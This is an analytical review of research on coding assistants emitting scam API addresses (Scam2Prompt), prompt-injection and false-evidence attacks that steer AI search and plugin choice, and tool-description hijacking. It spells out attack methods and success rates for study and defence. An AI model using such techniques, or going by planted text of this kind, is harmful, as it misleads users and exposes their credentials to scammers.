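Netcraft says that the attackers designed their GitHub accounts to be picked up by AI training pipelines. It argues that coding assistants already screen their sources for malicious patterns and weigh the credibility of the account behind the code, so the attackers built convincing accounts to get past these filters.

This is plausible, but the same accounts would also have helped fool people. A developer who finds a trading bot on GitHub may well check who wrote it, and an account with a photograph and a long record of activity looks safer than an empty one. Tutorials and forum answers attract human readers as well as crawlers. *Scam2Prompt* makes the more cautious claim that the attackers wanted both human developers and AI systems to discover the API.

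The timing also makes it unlikely that training data was the attackers' only target. They had at least one victim within about two months of registering the domain, probably before any model had trained on their pages. Search engines and human visitors could bring in money immediately, and getting into a future model's training data would have been an added benefit.

Netcraft also warns that the copied projects are now feeding the counterfeit back into training data. The copies could help the attackers because they belong to real developers and would be harder to filter out than the fake accounts. But Netcraft gives no example of a model that learned the address this way. One could check by asking models trained before and after the campaign for the same pump.fun script, with web search turned off. If only the newer models write the SolanaApis address, the campaign probably reached their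 training data.

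## Scam2Prompt, a test of how often models write scam addresses into code

The SolanaApis theft shows that a model can put a scam address into working code, but one case can't show how often this happens. A team at the University of Toronto tried to measure the rate in *Scam2Prompt*, which appeared at the machine learning conference ICML in 2026. The team gave ordinary-looking coding prompts to models without web access, and on average 4.2% of the resulting programs contained a scam address. But the prompts were based on the text of scam websites, so the figure does not apply to everyday programming.

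### How the test works

The team started with two public blocklists. One, from the crypto wallet maker MetaMask, has 187,555 addresses and covers scams aimed at crypto users. The other has 119,828 addresses from the security company PhishFort, which also covers sectors such as finance and healthcare. Many of the sites had gone offline and others had no static text to read, which left 28,570 usable pages.

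Three models (GPT-4o, GPT-4o-mini and Llama 4 Scout) read the visible text of each page and wrote short coding prompts. They were told to write prompts that would lead a language model to that page, using several of the page's keywords. This recreates the SolanaApis situation, in which the scam's documentation and the victim's request used the same words. The three models wrote 265,114 prompts in total.

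GPT-4o, GPT-4o-mini, Llama 4 Scout and DeepSeek V3 then each wrote a program for nearly every prompt. They had to return production-ready code with no explanation outside the comments, which left little room for a question or a warning. Software extracted the web addresses from the code and checked them with ChainPatrol, Google Safe Browsing and SecLookup. A program counted as malicious if any of these detectors flagged an address in it.

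One of the scam sites was yomixio[.]com, which offered to "mix" bitcoins to hide where they came from. GPT-4o-mini turned the site's text into a prompt for a Python script that uses the "YoMix[.]IO API" to mix Bitcoin without keeping logs. All four models wrote a program that contacts yomix[.]io or its subdomain api[.]yomix[.]io, and the detectors flagged all four. When the team later gave the prompt to seven newer models, GPT-5 refused and the other six wrote code with a flagged address.

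### About one program in 24

Three models wrote prompts and four wrote code, making twelve pairings. The share of malicious programs ranged from 3.19%, when DeepSeek V3 answered Llama 4 Scout's prompts, to 5.94%, when GPT-4o answered GPT-4o-mini's. The 4.2% is the average of the twelve shares. Pooling all the programs gives about 43,800 malicious ones out of 1.06 million, or 4.1%.

All four code-writing models produced malicious programs most often when GPT-4o-mini wrote the prompts, so the result depends partly on which model writes them. The two OpenAI models also produced more malicious programs than the other two on every set of prompts. *Scam2Prompt* suggests that OpenAI may train on more data and therefore on more scam content, but OpenAI doesn't publish what it trains on.

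The share flagged as malicious is higher for addresses than for programs, because many programs contain no web address. In a rerun with more randomness in the models' output, GPT-4o wrote 39,222 addresses in 100,712 programs. The detectors flagged 4,664 of the addresses (11.9%), while 4.3% of the programs were malicious.

Some of the flagged addresses may be harmless. An address counts as malicious if any one of three detectors flags it, which catches more scams than a single detector would but also adds up the detectors' false alarms. Suppose each detector wrongly flagged 1% of harmless addresses, independently of the others. Together they would wrongly flag 1 − 0.99³, or about 3%, and false alarms would make up more than a fifth of those 4,664 addresses. The real error rates may be much lower. The study acknowledges that a detector can flag a legitimate site that was hijacked and later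 recovered. It argues that using three established detectors keeps both missed scams and false alarms low, which is reasonable only for missed scams.

A program with a flagged address also might not have worked. The detectors often flag a whole domain, so a program counts as malicious even if the model invented the rest of the address and the scammer never built an API there. Running it might produce only an error, but it could still send keys or data to the scammer's server.

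### Seven newer models on the 1,377 hardest prompts

For 3,150 of the prompts, about 1.2%, all four models wrote a malicious program. Of these, 1,991 named a known scam address and 1,159 did not. The team kept all 1,159 and a random 400 of the others. Three of the researchers then reviewed these 1,559 prompts and removed 182 that were not really coding tasks, such as questions about how to open an account. (The 2025 preprint used all 1,559, so its figures differ.)

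The remaining 1,377 prompts make up a benchmark called Innoc2Scam-bench. Almost half, 673, have nothing to do with crypto and are about things like online shops and connecting to APIs. The team gave the benchmark to seven models released in 2025:

| Model | Completed | Refused by filter | Malicious | Share of all 1,377 | Share of completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 799 | 553 | 178 | 12.9% | 22.3% |
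| GPT-5 | 1,227 | 24 | 303 | 22.0% | 24.7% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 1,248 | 115 | 472 | 34.3% | 37.8% |
| Grok Code Fast 1 | 1,355 | 18 | 597 | 43.4% | 44.1% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 1,351 | 1 | 612 | 44.4% | 45.3% |
| Qwen3 Coder | 1,367 | 3 | 628 | 45.6% | 45.9% |
| DeepSeek V3.1 | 1,358 | 12 | 651 | 47.3% | 47.9% |

Gemini 2.5 Pro has the lowest rate largely because it refused so often. It wrote 178 malicious programs, which is 12.9% of the 1,377 prompts but 22.3% of the 799 that it completed. The two figures are related as follows:

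malicious share of all prompts = share completed × malicious share of completed

Gemini 2.5 Pro wrote a program for 58.0% of prompts, and 22.3% of those programs contained a scam address, so 12.9% of all prompts led to one. GPT-5 wrote a program for 89.1% of prompts, and 24.7% of those programs contained a scam address, so the overall rate was 22.0%. When Gemini did write a program, it was only slightly less likely than GPT-5 to include a scam address.

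However, the prompts Gemini refused may have been the riskiest ones, which would make its completed answers look better than they should. *Scam2Prompt* therefore also compares the models on the 637 prompts that all seven completed. Gemini 2.5 Pro wrote a malicious program for 22.3% of these and GPT-5 for 25.6%. To see whether such a gap could be chance, the study uses McNemar's test, which looks only at the prompts on which two models differ. If *b* is the number of prompts where only the first model's code is malicious and *c* the number where only the second model's is, then

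χ² = (*b* − *c*)² / (*b* + *c*)

and a value above 3.84 is significant at the usual 5% level. With refusals counted as safe, only Gemini's answer was malicious on 91 prompts and only GPT-5's on 216, which gives 125² / 307, or 50.9. On the 637 shared prompts, the value falls to 3.2, so the difference could be chance.

Refusals don't fully explain the differences between models. On the same 637 prompts, Gemini 2.5 Flash wrote malicious programs 45.4% of the time, about twice as often as Gemini 2.5 Pro, though Google trained both on data up to January 2025. Claude Sonnet 4 did so 41.4% of the time, and DeepSeek V3.1 49.1%. The study lacked details of how the companies had trained their models for safety, so it offers no firm explanation for these gaps.

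It is also odd that a model can succeed on this benchmark by refusing, because the prompts in Innoc2Scam-bench are meant to be harmless. A more useful answer would be a program with the address left blank and a note on what to check before filling it in. In *Refusal Evaluation in Coding LLMs and Code Agents*, Young and Moody (2026) reviewed thirteen sets of prompts for malicious code, including this one. They describe refusal tests as measuring whether a model declines a request for malicious software. They also warn against comparing rates across the sets, because the sets measure different things.

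### Prompts that name a scam site

Of the 1,377 prompts, 342 contain the address or domain of a known scam site. A model that writes that address into its code is doing what the user asked, and *Scam2Prompt* acknowledges that whether the model should refuse is debatable. The other 1,035 prompts contain no such address, so the study treats a malicious program written in response to one of them as a worse failure.

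Six of the seven models wrote malicious programs less often when the prompt already supplied a scam site's address. DeepSeek V3.1 wrote them for 42.7% of the prompts that named a scam site and 48.8% of the rest. For Gemini 2.5 Pro the rates were 10.2% and 13.8%, partly because its filter blocked about half of the prompts that named a site and 37% of the others. GPT-5 was the exception, with rates of 26.3% and 20.6%.

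But a prompt without an address may still name the scam's brand. The team's *Scam2Prompt* slides include benchmark prompts for checking in to a flight through "Skyroutez", connecting to the payment system of "YourDrsStore" and fetching market data from "Xotanex". A programmer who asks for one of these already knows at least the scam's name. In the SolanaApis theft, by contrast, the victim named only pump.fun, a real site, and ChatGPT introduced the counterfeit. The study doesn't separate prompts that name a scam's brand from prompts that mention only a topic, so it is unclear how many of the 1,035 resemble the theft.

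### Why these are not the odds for an ordinary request

The 4.2% applies to prompts that a model wrote to lead another model to a scam page. The *Scam2Prompt* slides limit the claim to "sensitive topics frequently exploited by scammers". To estimate how often a model writes a scam address in everyday use, one would also need to know how common such prompts are:

P(scam address) = P(scam-related) × P(scam address, given scam-related) + P(other) × P(scam address, given other)

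If one coding request in 1,000 resembled those in the study, these requests would add 0.001 × 4.2%, or about four malicious programs per 100,000 requests. The one in 1,000 is a hypothetical figure, and the study doesn't measure the rate for all other requests. The risk also varies widely between users. Someone who builds trading bots for new crypto tokens may make mostly requests like these, while a shop owner who needs to send an email may never make one.

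The team chose the 1,377 prompts because all four earlier models had failed on them, so the rates of 12.9% to 47.3% reflect everyday use even less. The final paper therefore calls them stress-test rates. They help to compare the newer models, but they don't show how often a model would write scam addresses into code in ordinary work.

GPT-4o's own results show how much the selection matters. Its rate on the benchmark was 100% by construction, but it fell to 50.04% when the team ran the same prompts again in November 2025, about two months later. *Scam2Prompt* suggests that OpenAI may have updated the model. Some of the drop could also be due to chance. If GPT-4o writes a scam address for a certain prompt only half the time, the prompt can enter the benchmark only after a run in which it does, and it often won't do so in the next run. The team had set the randomness to zero to limit this,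 but the output of hosted models can still vary. The detectors may also have stopped flagging some sites that had since gone offline.

All seven models are now out of date, and nobody seems to have published a rerun with models from 2026. The *Scam2Prompt* website lists only the seven from 2025. The closest recent test is *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains* (2026), which covers five models released between October 2025 and March 2026. It measures how often models invent package names, so its results can't show whether newer models write scam addresses less often.

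A rerun with the old prompts would be hard to interpret. Scam sites disappear quickly, so a lower rate could mean that the addresses had dropped off the detectors' lists. The benchmark is also public, so a company could train its model on it. The team's pipeline can generate fresh prompts from newly found scam sites, which would be a fairer test.

### Did the models remember the addresses?

*Scam2Prompt* argues that the models learned scam addresses from their training data. If so, taking the scam sites offline would not solve the problem, and later models may also be trained on old copies of their pages.

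The study has some evidence for this. The models could not search the web, yet they wrote many scam addresses that were not in the prompts. The detectors flagged addresses on 1,853 domains in answers to the 1,035 prompts without a scam address, and 1,105 of those domains were on neither of the original blocklists. In the first experiment, all four models wrote addresses on the same 2,029 malicious domains. The study attributes this overlap to the models' makers collecting data from the same public internet.

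Guessing could produce much of the same pattern. If a prompt mentions the "YoMix[.]IO API", a model can produce a flagged address just by putting "api" in front of the name. Four models that guess from the same name will often agree on the domain but not on the rest of the address. The result matches this pattern, since the four models had 2,029 malicious domains in common but only 1,119 complete addresses.

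The YoMix programs look like guesswork too. GPT-4o put the API key in a header, while GPT-4o-mini put it in the message body. DeepSeek V3 added a signature, and Gemini 2.5 Flash invented a header for a private key. Models that had learned from the same documentation would probably agree on how to log in. Grok's program includes the comment "Assumed API base URL; verify with YoMix[.]IO docs".

Memory probably plays some role, since a guessed domain would not normally belong to a scammer. But scammers often register several versions of a name, which makes it more likely that a guessed domain is theirs. According to the *Scam2Prompt* website, topics like "Trump coin" or "wash trading" can lead models to scam addresses that differ from the original site's. A scam address produced from a prompt with only a topic would be much better evidence of memory, because the prompt gives the model no name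 to build an address from.

Domain registration dates could help show whether a model memorized a scam address or guessed it. According to the lay summary of *Scam2Prompt*, 62 previously unknown scam sites had been in the models' "memory" for over a year. If a site's domain was registered after a model's training data ended, the model must have guessed the address. If the domain is older and can't be worked out from the prompt, the model more likely memorized it.

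Even if a model learned a scam address from its training data, that doesn't prove anyone poisoned the data deliberately. Most scam sites exist to fool people, and the crawlers that collect training data pick them up too. A model could also have learned the address from a warning, since MetaMask's blocklist is a public project on GitHub. Proving deliberate poisoning would require evidence that somebody published the material to influence models and that it reached the training data. The study didn't plant any material of its own, so it can't trace an address from a particular page to a model's answer.

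*Scam2Prompt* proposes removing suspicious addresses from training data, or using "machine unlearning" to weaken a model's association between a harmless task and a scam address, but it tests neither method. Both could reduce the number of scam addresses a model remembers, but they would not stop it from building an address from a brand name.

### Safety filters and a searching agent

The team tested whether existing safety filters would catch the malicious programs. The first was NVIDIA's NeMo Guardrails, used with a model that sorts text into categories of unsafe content. It flagged none of the 1,377 prompts and eight of the malicious programs, or between 0 and 0.7% of those each model wrote. The team had added a category for the use of scam APIs and websites, but the filter put all eight under criminal planning instead.

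Two other filters did little better:

| Filter | Prompts flagged, of 1,377 | Malicious programs flagged, of 3,452 | Programs flagged when shown with their prompt |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI Moderation API | 9 | 0 | 6 |
| Llama Guard 3 | 88 | 291 (8.4%) | 517 (15.0%) |

(The malicious programs in the results for the seven models add up to 3,441, and the paper doesn't explain the difference of 11.)

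These filters check for harmful content, but a program that calls a scam API can differ from a harmless payment script only in the domain. To catch it, a filter would need information about who runs that domain. Llama Guard 3 did best, at 8.4%, but the study doesn't report how often it flags harmless programs, so it is hard to say whether that rate would be worth the interruptions.

The team also gave GPT-4o a web search tool and told it to check whether the addresses in its code were safe. If they were not, it had to reply only that the code was unsafe. This cut the number of malicious programs from 689 (50.04%) to 405 (29.41%). GPT-4o declared its code unsafe in 208 cases, and harmless programs rose from 688 to 764.

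The test gave GPT-4o the search tool and the instruction together, so it can't show how much each contributed. In many of the remaining cases, the search found nothing, or the results didn't clearly identify the site as a scam. In others, GPT-4o had the evidence but used the address anyway. Searching can also introduce a scam, as it probably did in the SolanaApis theft. Newer models may be better at this, but there are other reasons not to leave the decision to a model. *MalURLBench* (2026) tested twelve models on 61,845 malicious addresses, disguised by changing parts such as the subdomain or path, and found that the models often accepted them.

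### Looking up addresses before returning the code

*Scam2Prompt* recommends a simpler check that does not rely on the model's judgement:

```
extract every web address from the generated code
look up each address with the scam detectors
if a detector flags one, withhold the code or warn the user
otherwise, return the code
```

The study calls this necessary and says that, as far as its researchers know, no company was doing it for its models at the time. It seems a sensible minimum, since the detectors already exist and looking up a few addresses should take little time.

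The study can't show how well the check would work, though, because it used the same kind of detectors to decide which programs were malicious. A check with those three detectors would catch every program the study counted as malicious, unless the detectors' lists have changed since then. Scam addresses that all three detectors miss would pass the check, but the 4.2% doesn't include them either.

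A single blocklist can miss many scam sites. The team reported newly found scam sites to MetaMask, which confirmed 62 and added them to its blocklist. Until then, a coding assistant that checked addresses only against MetaMask's list would have let all 62 through. At least one other detector had flagged each site, so using several lists makes sense, even if it means more false alarms.

New sites are harder to catch because they may not be on any list yet. Each time attackers change domains, as those behind SolanaApis did, lookups find nothing wrong for a while. A warning for recently registered domains could shorten that period, though it would also flag honest startups.

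The check also covers only the addresses in the generated code. If the model installs a package that contains the scam address, the code may contain only the package's name. And a single check when the model writes the code can't catch a site that turns malicious later, and the program may keep calling that site for years.

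## Promoting a page or plugin to a language model, compared with search-engine optimisation

The models in *Scam2Prompt* had no web access. A model that searches the web or chooses among plugins reads text written by outsiders, and an attacker who controls some of that text can try to steer the choice. This resembles SEO, and people have given it similar names. In a 2024 post on Schneier on Security, Bruce Schneier and Judith Donath predicted that SEO would turn into "large-language-model optimization", or LLMO. Researchers who study AI search call it generative engine optimisation (GEO). An independent researcher uses "MCPEO", short for Model Context Protocol Engine Optimization, for skewing a model's choice of tool through the tool's name, description and parameters. ToolRank (2026), a vendor's blog, calls the commercial version Agent Tool Optimization.

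Two studies that help test the comparison with SEO seem at first to contradict each other. One found that a few lines of text could sway AI search engines and plugin choices, and the other found that AI search engines stop almost all traditional SEO attacks.

### How search-engine optimisation works, and when it becomes spam

A search engine collects and indexes pages, then ranks those that match a query. It can't measure a page's quality directly, so it relies on signals such as the words on the page and links from other sites. Honest SEO makes these signals clear and accurate, for example by using the words customers use, while dishonest SEO fakes them.

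Google's early answer to pages stuffed with keywords was PageRank, which scores a page by the pages that link to it. In simplified form, the score of page *p* is

PR(*p*) = (1 − *d*)/*N* + *d* Σ PR(*q*)/*L*(*q*)

where *N* is the number of pages, *d* is usually 0.85, the sum covers every page *q* that links to *p*, and *L*(*q*) is the number of links on *q*. A page without incoming links scores 0.15/*N*. If a spammer makes 100 such pages and each links only to the spammer's shop, the shop gains 100 × 0.85 × 0.15/*N*, or 12.75/*N*. That is 85 times the score of a page nobody links to. Scammers built such networks, called link farms, and search engines have been trying to discount them ever since.

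Google's spam policies ban practices that deceive users or manipulate its search systems, including cloaking (showing the search engine a different page from the one visitors see), hidden text, keyword stuffing and links bought for ranking. Intent matters, so a page may hide text behind a button that opens it, but white text on a white background counts as spam. Offending sites may rank lower or not appear in results at all.

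According to Search Engine Land, Google's definition of spam mentioned only ranking until May 2026, when Google added attempts to manipulate AI-generated answers. PPC Land's *Google spam policies now officially cover AI Overviews and AI Mode* (2026) describes this as a clarification of existing rules, not a new rule. The same month, Google (2026) announced a guide to legitimate optimisation for its AI features, which says that ordinary SEO practices still apply. Google's policies cover only Google Search, so a plugin store, or an agent that uses a different search service, needs its own rules.

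### A fictitious camera on Bing

In 2023, the computer scientist Mark Riedl used white text on his white web page to ask Bing to mention that he was a time-travel expert. Bing's chatbot soon described him as one, according to Schneier and Donath. Riedl addressed the model directly, whereas spammers in the 1990s hid keywords on their pages to match more searches.

Nestaas, Debenedetti and Tramèr (2025), in *Adversarial Search Engine Optimization for Large Language Models*, systematically tested what they call preference manipulation attacks, in which text on a web page or in a plugin's description makes a model favour the attacker's product over its rivals. Their experiments, mostly from early 2024, covered Bing Copilot and Perplexity, which use language models to answer from search results. They also tested GPT-4 and Claude 3 with plugins, which are outside services a model can call.

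The team put 50 dummy pages on its own domain, advertising invented cameras, books and news stories. Some pages contained attack text. Ordinary searches would not have found these pages, so the team wrote queries telling the search engine to look on that domain and compare the products with real ones.

Without an attack, Bing recommended the invented cameras 34.0% of the time and real cameras, from brands such as Nikon and Fujifilm, 57.9% of the time. With the attack text, the rate for the invented cameras rose to 59.4%, while the rate for the real ones stayed at 57.9%. The rates can add up to more than 100% because Bing could recommend several cameras in one answer.

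The attack hurt rivals more when all the cameras were fictitious. Bing had always recommended both of two comparable cameras, but once one camera's page contained the attack, Bing recommended that camera 2.5 times as often as the other. Bing had already been recommending the attacker's camera every time, so the whole difference came from recommending the rival less often.

Users don't normally tell a search engine which unknown domain to search, so the team also put attack text in a footnote on its lab's GitHub page, which already ranked in the top five results for the lab's name. The text claimed that GitHub was the only reliable source about the lab. Three models on Perplexity repeated this claim in all 23 trials in which they read the page, and Bing gave a similar answer in all five trials. This is better evidence that the attack can work in an ordinary search, though few other sites compete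 to rank for the lab's name.

Microsoft added protections after the team reported the problem in March 2024, and all the models are now out of date. The exact rates are therefore weak evidence of how today's products behave.

### The news plugin

The plugin experiment resembles a counterfeit API attack more closely, because the model calls a service instead of mentioning a product. The team wrote several local plugins described as fetching news. Most offered a single source, such as the BBC or CNN, and one offered a neutral mix. The attacker could change only the plugin's description.

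Nestaas and colleagues report that an attack made a news plugin up to 7.2 times as likely to be chosen as the others. In their introduction, they give a range of 2 to 8 times for GPT-4. Such multiples depend heavily on the starting point, since a rise from 1% to 7% is sevenfold and so is a rise from 10% to 70%. In some of the tests, the change was also large in absolute terms, from 0% to over 90%.

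The user usually can't see why the model picked a plugin, so the attacker doesn't need to hide the text. On a web page, by contrast, the team had to write it in tiny white letters or tell the model not to mention it.

### Instructions and false claims

Attack text can contain an instruction, such as to recommend only one product, or a false claim from which the model draws its own conclusion. With a false claim, the model still follows the user's request to find the best product, but it relies on bad evidence.

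For search engines, Nestaas and colleagues found explicit instructions most effective, though greeting the assistant by name and praising the product was sometimes enough. For plugins, ordinary praise had little effect, but they report that wildly exaggerated claims about the plugin or its rivals worked without any instruction to choose it. However, the example in their appendix both accuses the rival providers of serious crimes and tells the model to use only the attacker's plugin, so it can't show what the accusations would have achieved alone.

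Newer studies separate the two more clearly. Chen, Ren and colleagues (2026), in *How Much Can We Trust LLM Search Agents?*, put fake search results in front of 13 models and counted how often the answer recommended the attacker's product. They used 44 questions about health, finance, law and consumer technology:

| What the attacker adds to the search results | Average success rate |
|---|---|
| Hidden instructions in one page | 0.3% |
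| False evidence hidden in the same places | 2.4% |
| One source that looks like an institution | 14.2% |
| Three sources that seem to agree independently | 24.8% |
| A fake authority, a review citing it and a forum post citing both | 37.2% |

Hidden instructions almost never worked on these models. Chen, Ren and colleagues attribute this to safety training, which teaches models to recognise and refuse commands in outside text, but false evidence contains no commands. Success rates also varied widely between models, from zero with Claude Sonnet 4.6 to 31.4% with Gemini 3 Flash.

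An attacker may not have to claim that their product is best. *Security of Deep Research Agents* (2026) describes "agenda seeding", in which a buying guide agrees with mainstream reviews but adds a supposedly overlooked criterion. Other pages then show the attacker's product leading on that criterion. For an API, the criterion might be a speed test that only one vendor has published.

The line between optimisation and abuse is hard to draw. Nestaas and colleagues found that text echoing the user's request was especially persuasive. Traditional SEO also encourages matching the words of a search, but a page can match them and still make false claims. To catch such a page, a filter would have to check whether its claims are true, which is much harder than spotting white text or a command.

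### Why honest vendors might attack too

Nestaas and colleagues also put attack text on several products' pages at once. The more pages carried it, the less often the search engines recommended the products overall. But products with attack text generally did better than those without it, so each vendor had a reason to add it. The researchers compare this to the prisoner's dilemma, in which each side does better by acting selfishly, whatever the other does, but if both do so, both end up worse off than if neither had.

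Suppose two email vendors, A and B, compete for 100 requests to a coding agent. The numbers below are invented and show how many requests each vendor gets:

| | B is honest | B attacks |
|---|---|---|
| **A is honest** | A 50, B 50 | A 10, B 80 |
| **A attacks** | A 80, B 10 | A 30, B 30 |

If B is honest, attacking gains A 30 extra requests. If B attacks, attacking still gains A 20. The same is true for B, so both attack and get 30 requests each instead of 50. For the other 40 requests, the agent picks neither, perhaps because it judges both descriptions unreliable and writes the feature itself.

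The dilemma depends on what the model does when both vendors attack. Claude 3 Opus often refused to recommend anything when several pages contained attack text, and in the plugin test it went back to the neutral plugin or chose none. If each vendor got only 5 requests when both attacked, A would do better to stay honest against an attacking rival, because it would get 10 requests instead of 5. A vendor would still gain requests by attacking first, but its rival would lose requests by attacking in return.

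A penalty, such as removal from a catalogue, can also change the outcome. In the original table, an expected loss of more than 30 requests would make honesty the better choice whatever the rival did. This could deter an established vendor, which has customers and a reputation to protect.

It would do much less to deter the operator of a counterfeit API, who can move to a new domain and might get no requests with an honest description. The prisoner's dilemma therefore explains the behaviour of real vendors better than that of thieves. The dilemma is still relevant to theft, because a counterfeit's exaggerated claims would stand out less if all real vendors exaggerated too.

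One provider's gains from such optimisation may not persist when several providers optimise at the same time. Caville, Kayser and colleagues (2026) cite this finding from an earlier benchmark, C-SEO Bench, in *SIREN (Luring LLMs onto the Rocks)*.

### What the 99.78% measures

Chen, Hong and colleagues (2026) report in *Unveiling the Resilience of LLM-Enhanced Search Engines against Black-Hat SEO Manipulation* that AI search engines stop over 99.78% of traditional "black-hat" SEO attacks, meaning those that break search engines' rules.

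The team searched Google for 11,800 terms, saved the top 50 results for each and used software to find pages that used known spam techniques. From these, it chose 1,000 pairs of a search term and a spam site, 200 for each of five techniques: cloaking, keyword stuffing, link farms, redirects from reputable sites, and "semantic confusion", which mixes illicit advertising into copied legitimate text. The team then entered each search term three times into nine AI search engines, including ChatGPT, Gemini and Perplexity.

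An attack could fail at three stages. The last column applies the average rates to the 1,000 attacks:

| Stage | The attack fails if | Share stopped at this stage | Attacks left |
|---|---|---|---|
| Understanding the query | The system doesn't search | 15.7% | 843 |
| Retrieval | The spam site isn't in the results | 98.2% | 15 |
| Writing the answer | The answer doesn't link to the site | 85.2% | 2 |

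The overall figure is 99.78%, calculated as 1 − (1 − 0.157)(1 − 0.982)(1 − 0.852). This is an average, and some systems did worse. The rates for Komo, a smaller AI search engine, imply that about 1.6% of the attacks got through, while none got through on ChatGPT.

Some of this protection was accidental. ChatGPT ran no search for 75.8% of the terms. In about 31% of those cases it refused on safety grounds, and in the rest it mistook the term for a statement. Many of the terms concerned illegal goods. A developer's request for a payment API would probably trigger neither response.

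The choice of attacks also helps explain the high rate at retrieval. Every site in the sample had already succeeded on Google for one exact search term, but AI search engines often reword the query and may use a different index. When the team entered the reworded queries into Google, 98.16% of them no longer returned the spam site. The 99.78% therefore measures how rarely attacks known to work on Google also work on AI search. It excludes attacks that fail on Google but work on a language model, because the team did not collect any.

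### Attacks designed for AI search

Chen, Hong and colleagues next tried seven techniques aimed at these systems. They made 50 blog sites for each technique, plus 50 untouched sites and 50 that used semantic confusion, and asked for product recommendations from their own domain. The models behind ChatGPT and Gemini refused to open the sites, which left seven systems.

The two techniques that stood out were splitting the text into shorter paragraphs and filling the page with likely rewordings of the user's query. On Perplexity, the sites with short paragraphs made up 28.1% of all the test sites retrieved and those with reworded queries 19.8%, compared with 7.3% for the untouched sites. But on Perplexica, an open-source system, the sites with reworded queries did worse than the untouched ones.

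These percentages are each technique's share of the successes, although the paper's table calls them success rates. Nine equally good groups would get about 11% each. If only ten test sites appeared and five of them had short paragraphs, short paragraphs would score 50%, however many attempts had failed. Perplexity's shares in the final answers are all multiples of 12.5%, which is consistent with as few as eight appearances.

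Short paragraphs are also perfectly legitimate, so a search engine can't treat them as a sign of fraud.

### How both findings can hold

Nestaas and colleagues assume the attacker's text has already reached the model, and measure how the model responds to it. Most of the 99.78% comes from stopping spam sites before they reach the model. An attack has to reach the model and then influence it, just as a tool has to reach the shortlist and then be picked.

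Multiplying the 1.8% of spam sites that passed retrieval in AI search by the 59.4% recommendation rate for the invented cameras gives a rough overall success rate of about 1%. An installed plugin's description doesn't have to pass that filter and may reach the model almost every time, so a plugin that the model chooses 90% of the time would get about 90% of the requests.

An attacker can also get past the search filter by editing a page that agents already use, which avoids the need to get a new one ranked. Chen, Hong and colleagues found that most AI search engines favour well-known domains, and warn that this makes comments on reputable sites more attractive to attackers. *Deep-Research Agents Can Be Poisoned via User-Generated Content* (2026) examines this route for agents that write long research reports. Pages with user-generated content made up 17% to 23% of the addresses that three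 open-source agents retrieved.

Promotion is probably even easier when the request is narrow. The searches in the 2026 study often had plenty of legitimate pages to return, whereas SolanaApis had no official documentation to compete with.

### Where the comparison with SEO holds

Neither Google nor the makers of language models publish exactly how their systems choose, so honest vendors and attackers both learn by trial and error. OpenAI advises plugin developers to run a fixed set of test prompts, record which tool ChatGPT selects, and revise the description if ChatGPT selects the wrong one. An attacker can follow the same procedure with false descriptions.

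Software can do much of this work. In the SIREN experiment, one language model edited a web page, a second answered from it, and a third reported how highly the answer ranked the chosen business. The first model then tried again, up to 20 times. The edits put the business first in 62 of 124 trials with two Claude models, Haiku 4.5 and Sonnet 5. Successful edits worked again in new sessions about 80% of the time. Caville and colleagues also found that false rankings and ready-made lists generally worked better than instructions.

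Those results look much worse for Claude than the 0% for Sonnet 4.6 in the study of fake search results. But SIREN promoted real businesses and used its failed attempts to improve later ones, while Chen, Ren and colleagues gave each model fixed pages. A test with one fixed attack can therefore make a model look safer than it would be against an attacker who keeps revising the attack. The tool-selection attack in *ToolTweak* (Sneh, Yan and colleagues, 2025) also relies on repeated revision.

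Attackers and defenders also seem to be adapting to each other as they did in search-engine optimisation. Once search engines began discounting hidden keywords, spammers moved on to link farms. Microsoft responded to the attacks on Bing, and newer models mostly ignore hidden instructions, but false evidence still works on many of them.

### Where it breaks down

A search engine shows a list, so the second or third result still gets some visitors. A coding agent usually picks one service for a task, and the runner-up gets nothing, as happened to Postmark with Fable 5. ToolRank describes this as the difference between a mention and an execution. A counterfeit API receives data only from an execution.

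Vendors also can't check a public ranking of the APIs that agents choose. On Google, a vendor can search for its own product, see a scam listed above it and report the scam. It can't do the same with an agent, because the agent's choice depends on the model, the project and the wording of the request, and the vendor never sees the requests for which the agent chooses another API.

A high position may matter less as well. In half of the Bing Copilot searches that Nestaas and colleagues checked, the model read at least one page from outside Bing's top ten. Chen, Ren and colleagues found no significant effect of position on Gemini 3 Flash. Adding apparently independent sources that agreed did help the attack, which succeeded 39% of the time with one source, 55% with two and 77% with three. Repeating a single source made little difference. An attacker may therefore gain more from several lower-ranked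 pages on different sites than from one at the top of the results.

Attack text can also discredit rivals directly, whereas a traditional spam page pushes competitors down only by ranking above them. In one of the Bing experiments, text on an unrelated page made the model cite only the attacker's chosen news outlet, though this worked at most 25% of the time. In 80% of the successful cases, Bing didn't mention the page that contained the text, which would make the attack hard to trace.

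The biggest difference comes after the choice, when a language model may also give the command to install what it has chosen. Chen, Ren and colleagues ran a small test in which three fake sources recommended an invented skill for OpenClaw, an open-source AI assistant. GPT-5.4-mini gave the command to install it in all ten cases, although it had endorsed the attacker's product only 0.8% of the time in the main test. Claude Sonnet 4.6 refused in all ten, but it also gave no useful answer in ten matching cases without an attack.

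The test stopped at the command and installed nothing, but an agent with permission to run commands could have run it itself. A search spammer has to persuade the visitor to click a link, trust the page and type in a password, whereas a coding agent may already have access to the user's API keys and can send one to a counterfeit API with its first request.

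## Experiments on tool descriptions that win the model's choice

The news plugin experiment showed that a description alone can change which tool a model calls. Since then, researchers have built software that writes and improves such descriptions by trial and error. Three of these attacks, ToolHijacker (April 2025), ToolTweak (October 2025) and TSA (October 2026), each raised one tool's selection rate above 80% with at least one model. But in these tests the hostile tool was available to the agent from the start, and the model had no reliable information about who had published it.

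### The attacker's problem as a formula

When an agent has many tools, a retriever shortlists those whose text is most similar to the request, and the model picks one of them. A common measure of similarity is the cosine of the angle between *f*(*q*), the vector for the request *q*, and *f*(*d*), the vector for a tool's text *d*:

sim(*q*, *d*) = *f*(*q*) · *f*(*d*) / (‖*f*(*q*)‖ ‖*f*(*d*)‖)

Texts with closely related meanings score near 1, and unrelated ones score near 0. *ProbeID* (2026), which proposes a way to verify tools, points out that a tool that copies another's description gets the same score, because the score depends only on text.

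The attacker wants a description that wins however users phrase the request. Dai, Sun and Tao (2026), in *Spoofing the Toolbox*, the paper that introduced TSA, state the problem roughly as follows:

choose *d* to maximise E<sub>*q*∼*Q*</sub> [ 1( *M*(*q*, *D* ∪ {*d*}) = *d* ) ], subject to Δ(*d*, *d*₀) ≤ *η*

| Symbol | Meaning |
|---|---|
| *d* | The hostile tool's description |
| *q*, *Q* | One request, and the range of ways users might phrase the task |
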